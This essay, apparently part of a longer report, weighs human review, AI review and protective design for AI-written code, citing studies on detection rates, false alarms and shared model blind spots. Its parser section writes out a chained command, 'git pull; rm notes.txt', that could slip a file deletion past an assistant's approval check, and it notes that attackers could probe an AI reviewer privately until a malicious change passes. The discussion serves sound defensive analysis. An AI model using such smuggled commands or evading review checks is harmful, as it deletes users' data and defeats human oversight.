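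Haynes argues that the economics of review get worse as models improve. By his own assumptions, the total cost of a secure patch, including review, still fell by 5%, from about $133 with the older Claude Opus 5 to $126 with Fable 5.1. The computing cost per secure patch fell by 47%. Opus 5 had used $1,116 of computing to produce about 132 working patches, 58 of them secure.

### What reviewers miss

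These calculations assume that a reviewer who reads a patch will notice the flaw. In *Less is More*, Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022) asked developers to review a change with two security flaws. The code put sensitive data into an error message and scrambled passwords with MD5, an outdated method that attackers can break quickly. Of 33 reviewers without special instructions, one noticed the exposed data and seven noticed MD5. Of 41 told to look for security problems, 19 noticed the data and 25 noticed MD5. Giving reviewers a security checklist as well made no significant difference.

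Reviewers find familiar flaws more easily. In *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?* (2021), 65% of reviewers found a database injection, but only 14 of 66 found a less familiar failure to check user input. The researchers then told the others that the code contained a vulnerability, and 45 of them still missed it.

In Braz and colleagues' experiment, the best detection rate among reviewers given only the security instruction was 61%. At that rate, reviewers would miss about 35 of Fable 5.1's 89 insecure patches, after $7,800 of reading. This is a rough estimate because the flaws differ from those in the experiment. But a budget for human review should include time to look specifically for security problems, because general instructions to review the code produced much worse results.

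Reviewers under pressure probably do worse than participants in an experiment. *AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026) followed 802 developers at a software company that had set out to double its output with AI. Changes per reviewer roughly doubled, and reviewers increasingly approved changes without comment. The company did not have to undo or repair a larger share of changes afterwards. This is some evidence that the lighter review did little harm, although a security flaw or untidy code may not lead to a repair for years.

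Projects accept some coding agents' changes so quickly that a person can hardly have read them carefully. *For Coding Agents, the Repository Matters* (2026) examined a selected set of agents' changes and found that 57.7% of the accepted ones were merged within six minutes. A person reading 500 lines an hour can read 50 lines in that time. Some of these merges may have been automatic.

Labelling code as AI-written may not make people read it more thoroughly. In *Same Scrutiny, More Time*, Khojah, de Oliveira Neto and colleagues (2026) tracked the eyes of 32 practitioners as they reviewed human-written code that was sometimes labelled as AI-written. The participants looked at labelled code for up to 60% longer, but their eye movements showed no sign that they inspected it in more detail.

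### AI reviewers and shared blind spots

AI systems can read far more code than people can, but Zietsman (2026) argues that they often lack anything to check it against. Without a specification, an AI system reviewing another's program can only compare the code with itself and with what the reviewer learned in training. Two models with similar training are likely to overlook the same mistakes. If each misses half of all defects, together they miss a quarter when their misses are independent, but the second review adds nothing when they miss exactly the same defects.

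Zietsman tested AI reviewers on small functions that each contained one planted bug. Claude found all five textbook errors, such as a wrong leap-year rule, in every attempt. It did worse on rules that people in a particular profession know but the code doesn't reveal. One function swapped the fuel reserves required for jet and piston aircraft. Claude missed the error in all five attempts and defended the swapped values as correct, while Google's Gemini found it every time. In 20 attempts altogether, none of four AI reviewers noticed that another function broke a rule about which medical codes can describe a patient's main diagnosis.

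Tests written from the rules caught every bug, but this part of the comparison is unfair because whoever wrote the tests knew where the bugs were. A human programmer without medical training would probably have missed the diagnosis rule too. The experiments are tiny, but they support the narrower claim that a reviewer needs access to the rule and that a different model helps only if it happens to have learned it.

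Larger experiments suggest that the reviewer's ability matters at least as much as its independence. Xiang, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Cross-Model LLM Code Review*, had two models write solutions to 116 programming-contest problems and then review and correct them without running them:

| Author | Reviewer | Correct before | Correct after | Repaired | Broken |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | Claude Opus 4.7 | 71.6% | 89.7% | 26 | 5 |
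| GPT-5.5 | GPT-5.5 | 71.6% | 84.5% | 21 | 6 |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | Claude Opus 4.7 | 91.4% | 91.4% | 3 | 3 |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | GPT-5.5 | 91.4% | 82.8% | 3 | 13 |

GPT-5.5 repaired many of its own mistakes, so reviewing one's own work can be useful. When it reviewed the stronger model's work, it broke more programs than it repaired. All the reviewers could see the problem statement, so they had the kind of reference that Zietsman recommends.

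*When Does a Second Model Help?* (Song, 2026) tested reviews on 150 errors planted in programs, tutorials and presentation scripts written by Claude. Two separate reviews by Claude together found 42.7% of the errors, while one by Claude and one by GPT-5.4 found 56.7%. GPT-5.4 may simply have been the better reviewer, since two reviews by GPT-5.4 did not do significantly worse than the mixed pair. Claude and GPT-5.4 both missed 65 of the errors, compared with about 54 if their misses had been independent, so using a different model reduces the overlap but does not remove it.

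### False alarms

A detection rate means little without the rate of false alarms, because a reviewer that objects to everything finds every defect. *What Moves the Ceiling on Automated Audit* (Dong, 2026) measured both rates on short Python functions written by an older Claude model. All the functions had passed the visible tests, but some failed hidden ones. One reading by GPT-5.6 Terra caught 10.7% of the faulty functions. Eight readings together caught 30.0% but also objected to 16.0% of the correct ones.

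Suppose a team submits 1,000 such functions, of which 100 are faulty. Eight readings would flag 30 of the faulty functions and miss the other 70. They would also flag 144 correct functions, so only about one in six flagged functions would be faulty.

Dong also tried a stronger Claude model as the reviewer. It blocked only about 4% of the faulty functions and 3.3% of the correct ones. When Dong counted its minor remarks as well as its blocking objections, it flagged 59.1% of the faulty functions and 34.0% of the correct ones, compared with 34.5% and 19.3% for GPT-5.6 Terra. The Claude model flagged more functions but rated fewer of the problems it reported as serious. The two models ran with different settings, so this is not a clean comparison of their abilities. Still, teams should test how serious a problem must be for a reviewer to block the code before they conclude that the reviewer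 cannot detect it.

Three groups of AI reviewers all missed 57 faulty functions. Two AI raters judged that the specification did not determine the right answer for 44 of them. This fits Zietsman's argument. More AI review would not settle such cases reliably, because somebody first has to decide what the function should do.

### Finding flaws in existing code

Companies report better results from reviewers adapted to their own code. InfoQ's *How Figma Uses AI Agents for Security* (2026) and tl;dr sec's *Anthropic and Meta Agents be Hackin', Agentic Incident Response Notebooks* summarise an article by the design-software company Figma about its system. Figma's engineers hand-labelled the false alarms from eight weeks of changes and used them to improve the reviewer's instructions. The share of correct alarms rose from 15% to 80%. A further review step raised detection by about 30%.

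Figma runs Claude Code and Codex side by side as code reviewers because they catch different bugs. Together they caught 75.8% of 66 real vulnerabilities that human reviewers and conventional scanners had missed. They also found more than 100 previously unknown flaws in existing code, two of them critical. These are Figma's own measurements, and the 75.8% may overstate how well the tools catch new kinds of flaws, because Figma updates the tools' instructions whenever it discovers a bug.

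Frontier models now find flaws faster than people can deal with them. In a talk published by AI Engineer (2026), a speaker from Anthropic described a scan of more than a thousand open-source projects. It produced 23,000 possible flaws, of which 6,200 were provisionally rated high or critical. Of 1,752 candidates assessed, 1,094 kept a high or critical rating. At the time of the update, Anthropic had reported 1,600 possible flaws to maintainers, and about 100 had a fix. Nobody knows how many flaws these projects contain, so the scan's detection rate is unknown.

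Confirming a flaw with a working attack can save people from reading false alarms. Theori's scan of 28 AI-written applications produced 8,827 detections. Help Net Security reports that the company merged duplicates and built example exploits for the rest, which left 434. But an exploit cannot reveal flaws the scanner missed.

AI review alone may not relieve overloaded teams. Newman, Bird and colleagues (2026) surveyed 2,590 developers at a large software company for *Level Up! AI-Driven Challenges and Adaptations to Code Review Practices*. Those who used AI for review did not find it easier to keep up, perhaps because the busiest developers are the most likely to try it. But 71% said their own reviewing had shifted towards design and intent, which is a sensible use of people's time if the AI reviewer's detection rate is known.

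### Designs that leave less to read

Developers can also reduce the amount of code that has to be right. Suppose a shop uses 50,000 lines of AI-written code to read complaints and decide on refunds. At 400 lines an hour, one reading would take 125 hours. The shop can instead require every refund to go through this function:

```python
def pay_refund(order_id, amount):
    with database.lock(order_id):
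        order = database.load(order_id)
        if not 0 < amount <= order.paid - order.refunded:
            raise ValueError("refund exceeds payment")
        order.refunded += amount
        database.save(order)
        bank.send(order.account, amount)
```

The other code supplies only an order number and an amount. It cannot choose the account or refund more than the customer paid. The lock prevents two simultaneous requests from both passing the check. A reviewer can read this function in a few minutes, but must also confirm that the rest of the program cannot reach the bank or the database any other way. Any Python code in the same program could call `bank.send` directly, so in practice `pay_refund` has to run as a separate program with its own password for the bank.

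A small trusted core with a narrow interface leaves less code to read. The seL4 kernel applies this principle to a whole computer. Memory-safe languages also reduce how much code people need to read. Adobe's *Strengthening product safeguards with AI* describes isolating the code that parses risky files, so that a flaw there does less damage while developers prepare a fix.

The unread code can still do harm within its limits. It might deny refunds to every honest customer or grant them to every dishonest one. If the shop has 1,000 recent orders of $40, the most it can lose by refunding them is $40,000. A daily limit in `pay_refund` would reduce the possible loss further, and the owner can choose that limit without understanding how the unread code processes complaints.

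### A parser whose author rarely reads it

Stannard's *Software 2.0* describes a project where the unread code affects security. ShellSyntaxTree is a parser, a program that works out the structure of text, in this case operating system commands. An AI assistant called Netclaw uses it to decide which commands need a person's approval. If the user has already approved a pattern such as `git pull`, Netclaw runs matching commands without asking. A parser that overlooked the second half of `git pull; rm notes.txt` could let the assistant delete a file without permission.

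Stannard has let a coding agent work on the parser for two and a half days without supervision, and gives three reasons for trusting the result:

- The task is narrow. The parser identifies the parts of a command but does not judge whether the command is safe. If a command is too complex to analyse, the parser reports this instead of guessing.
- Checking is cheap. Thousands of example commands, many from real use, run in under a minute, and the whole collection runs again after every change.
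- Feedback is fast. Stannard also develops Netclaw, so he can try each new version there and add any failures to the collection.

Many file converters, calculators and compression programs meet the first two conditions. Stannard says that most software does not qualify, particularly applications with user data, secrets and connections to other systems, and that people should read most AI-written code.

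The third condition is weaker than it looks, even for his parser. Users notice at once when Netclaw asks for approval unnecessarily, but no prompt alerts them when it wrongly runs a command without asking. The example commands also come mostly from ordinary use, whereas an attacker would look for an unusual command that the parser misreads. Stannard calls his method verification rather than testing, but concedes that it cannot cover every possible command.

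A simpler design would approve only commands that exactly match an entry on a list. It would need no parser and almost no reading, but the user would have to approve `git pull origin main` separately from `git pull`. The parser avoids these interruptions but adds some risk, and whether that is worthwhile depends on what else the assistant can do on the computer.

### How each approach fails

| | Typical failure | How far it can spread |
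|---|---|---|
| Human reading | A hurried or unsuspecting reviewer approves a flaw | Usually one change at a time |
| AI review | The model overlooks the same kind of flaw again and again | Every program that relies on that model |
| Protective design | The boundary has a gap, or the core contains a mistake | All the code and data that the boundary should protect |

A review that misses a flaw looks the same as a review of code that has none, whether the reviewer is a person or an AI system. Teams can measure how often reviewers miss flaws by planting known ones in copies of their code, as the experiments did. For AI reviewers, they should vary the kinds of flaw, since repeating the same review may add little. In Dong's study, the stronger Claude model read each of 110 faulty functions eight times, and its verdict varied for only 3 of them. An attacker with access to the same model could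 also try malicious changes in private until one passed.

When the design works, failures are often visible. The bank refuses a payment or the operating system blocks access to a file, and the owners can investigate. A gap in the boundary may do more harm than a missed flaw in ordinary code, because nobody has read the code behind it. The boundary and the core therefore deserve the most careful human reading, as well as AI review and attempts to break them.

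*Automating Low-Risk Code Review at Meta* (2026) describes a system Meta uses to automate review only for changes that meet conservative safety criteria. If a team could similarly leave 120 of Endor Labs' 156 patches to automatic checks, reviewers could spend two hours on each of the other 36 for $7,200, compared with $7,800 for half an hour on every patch.
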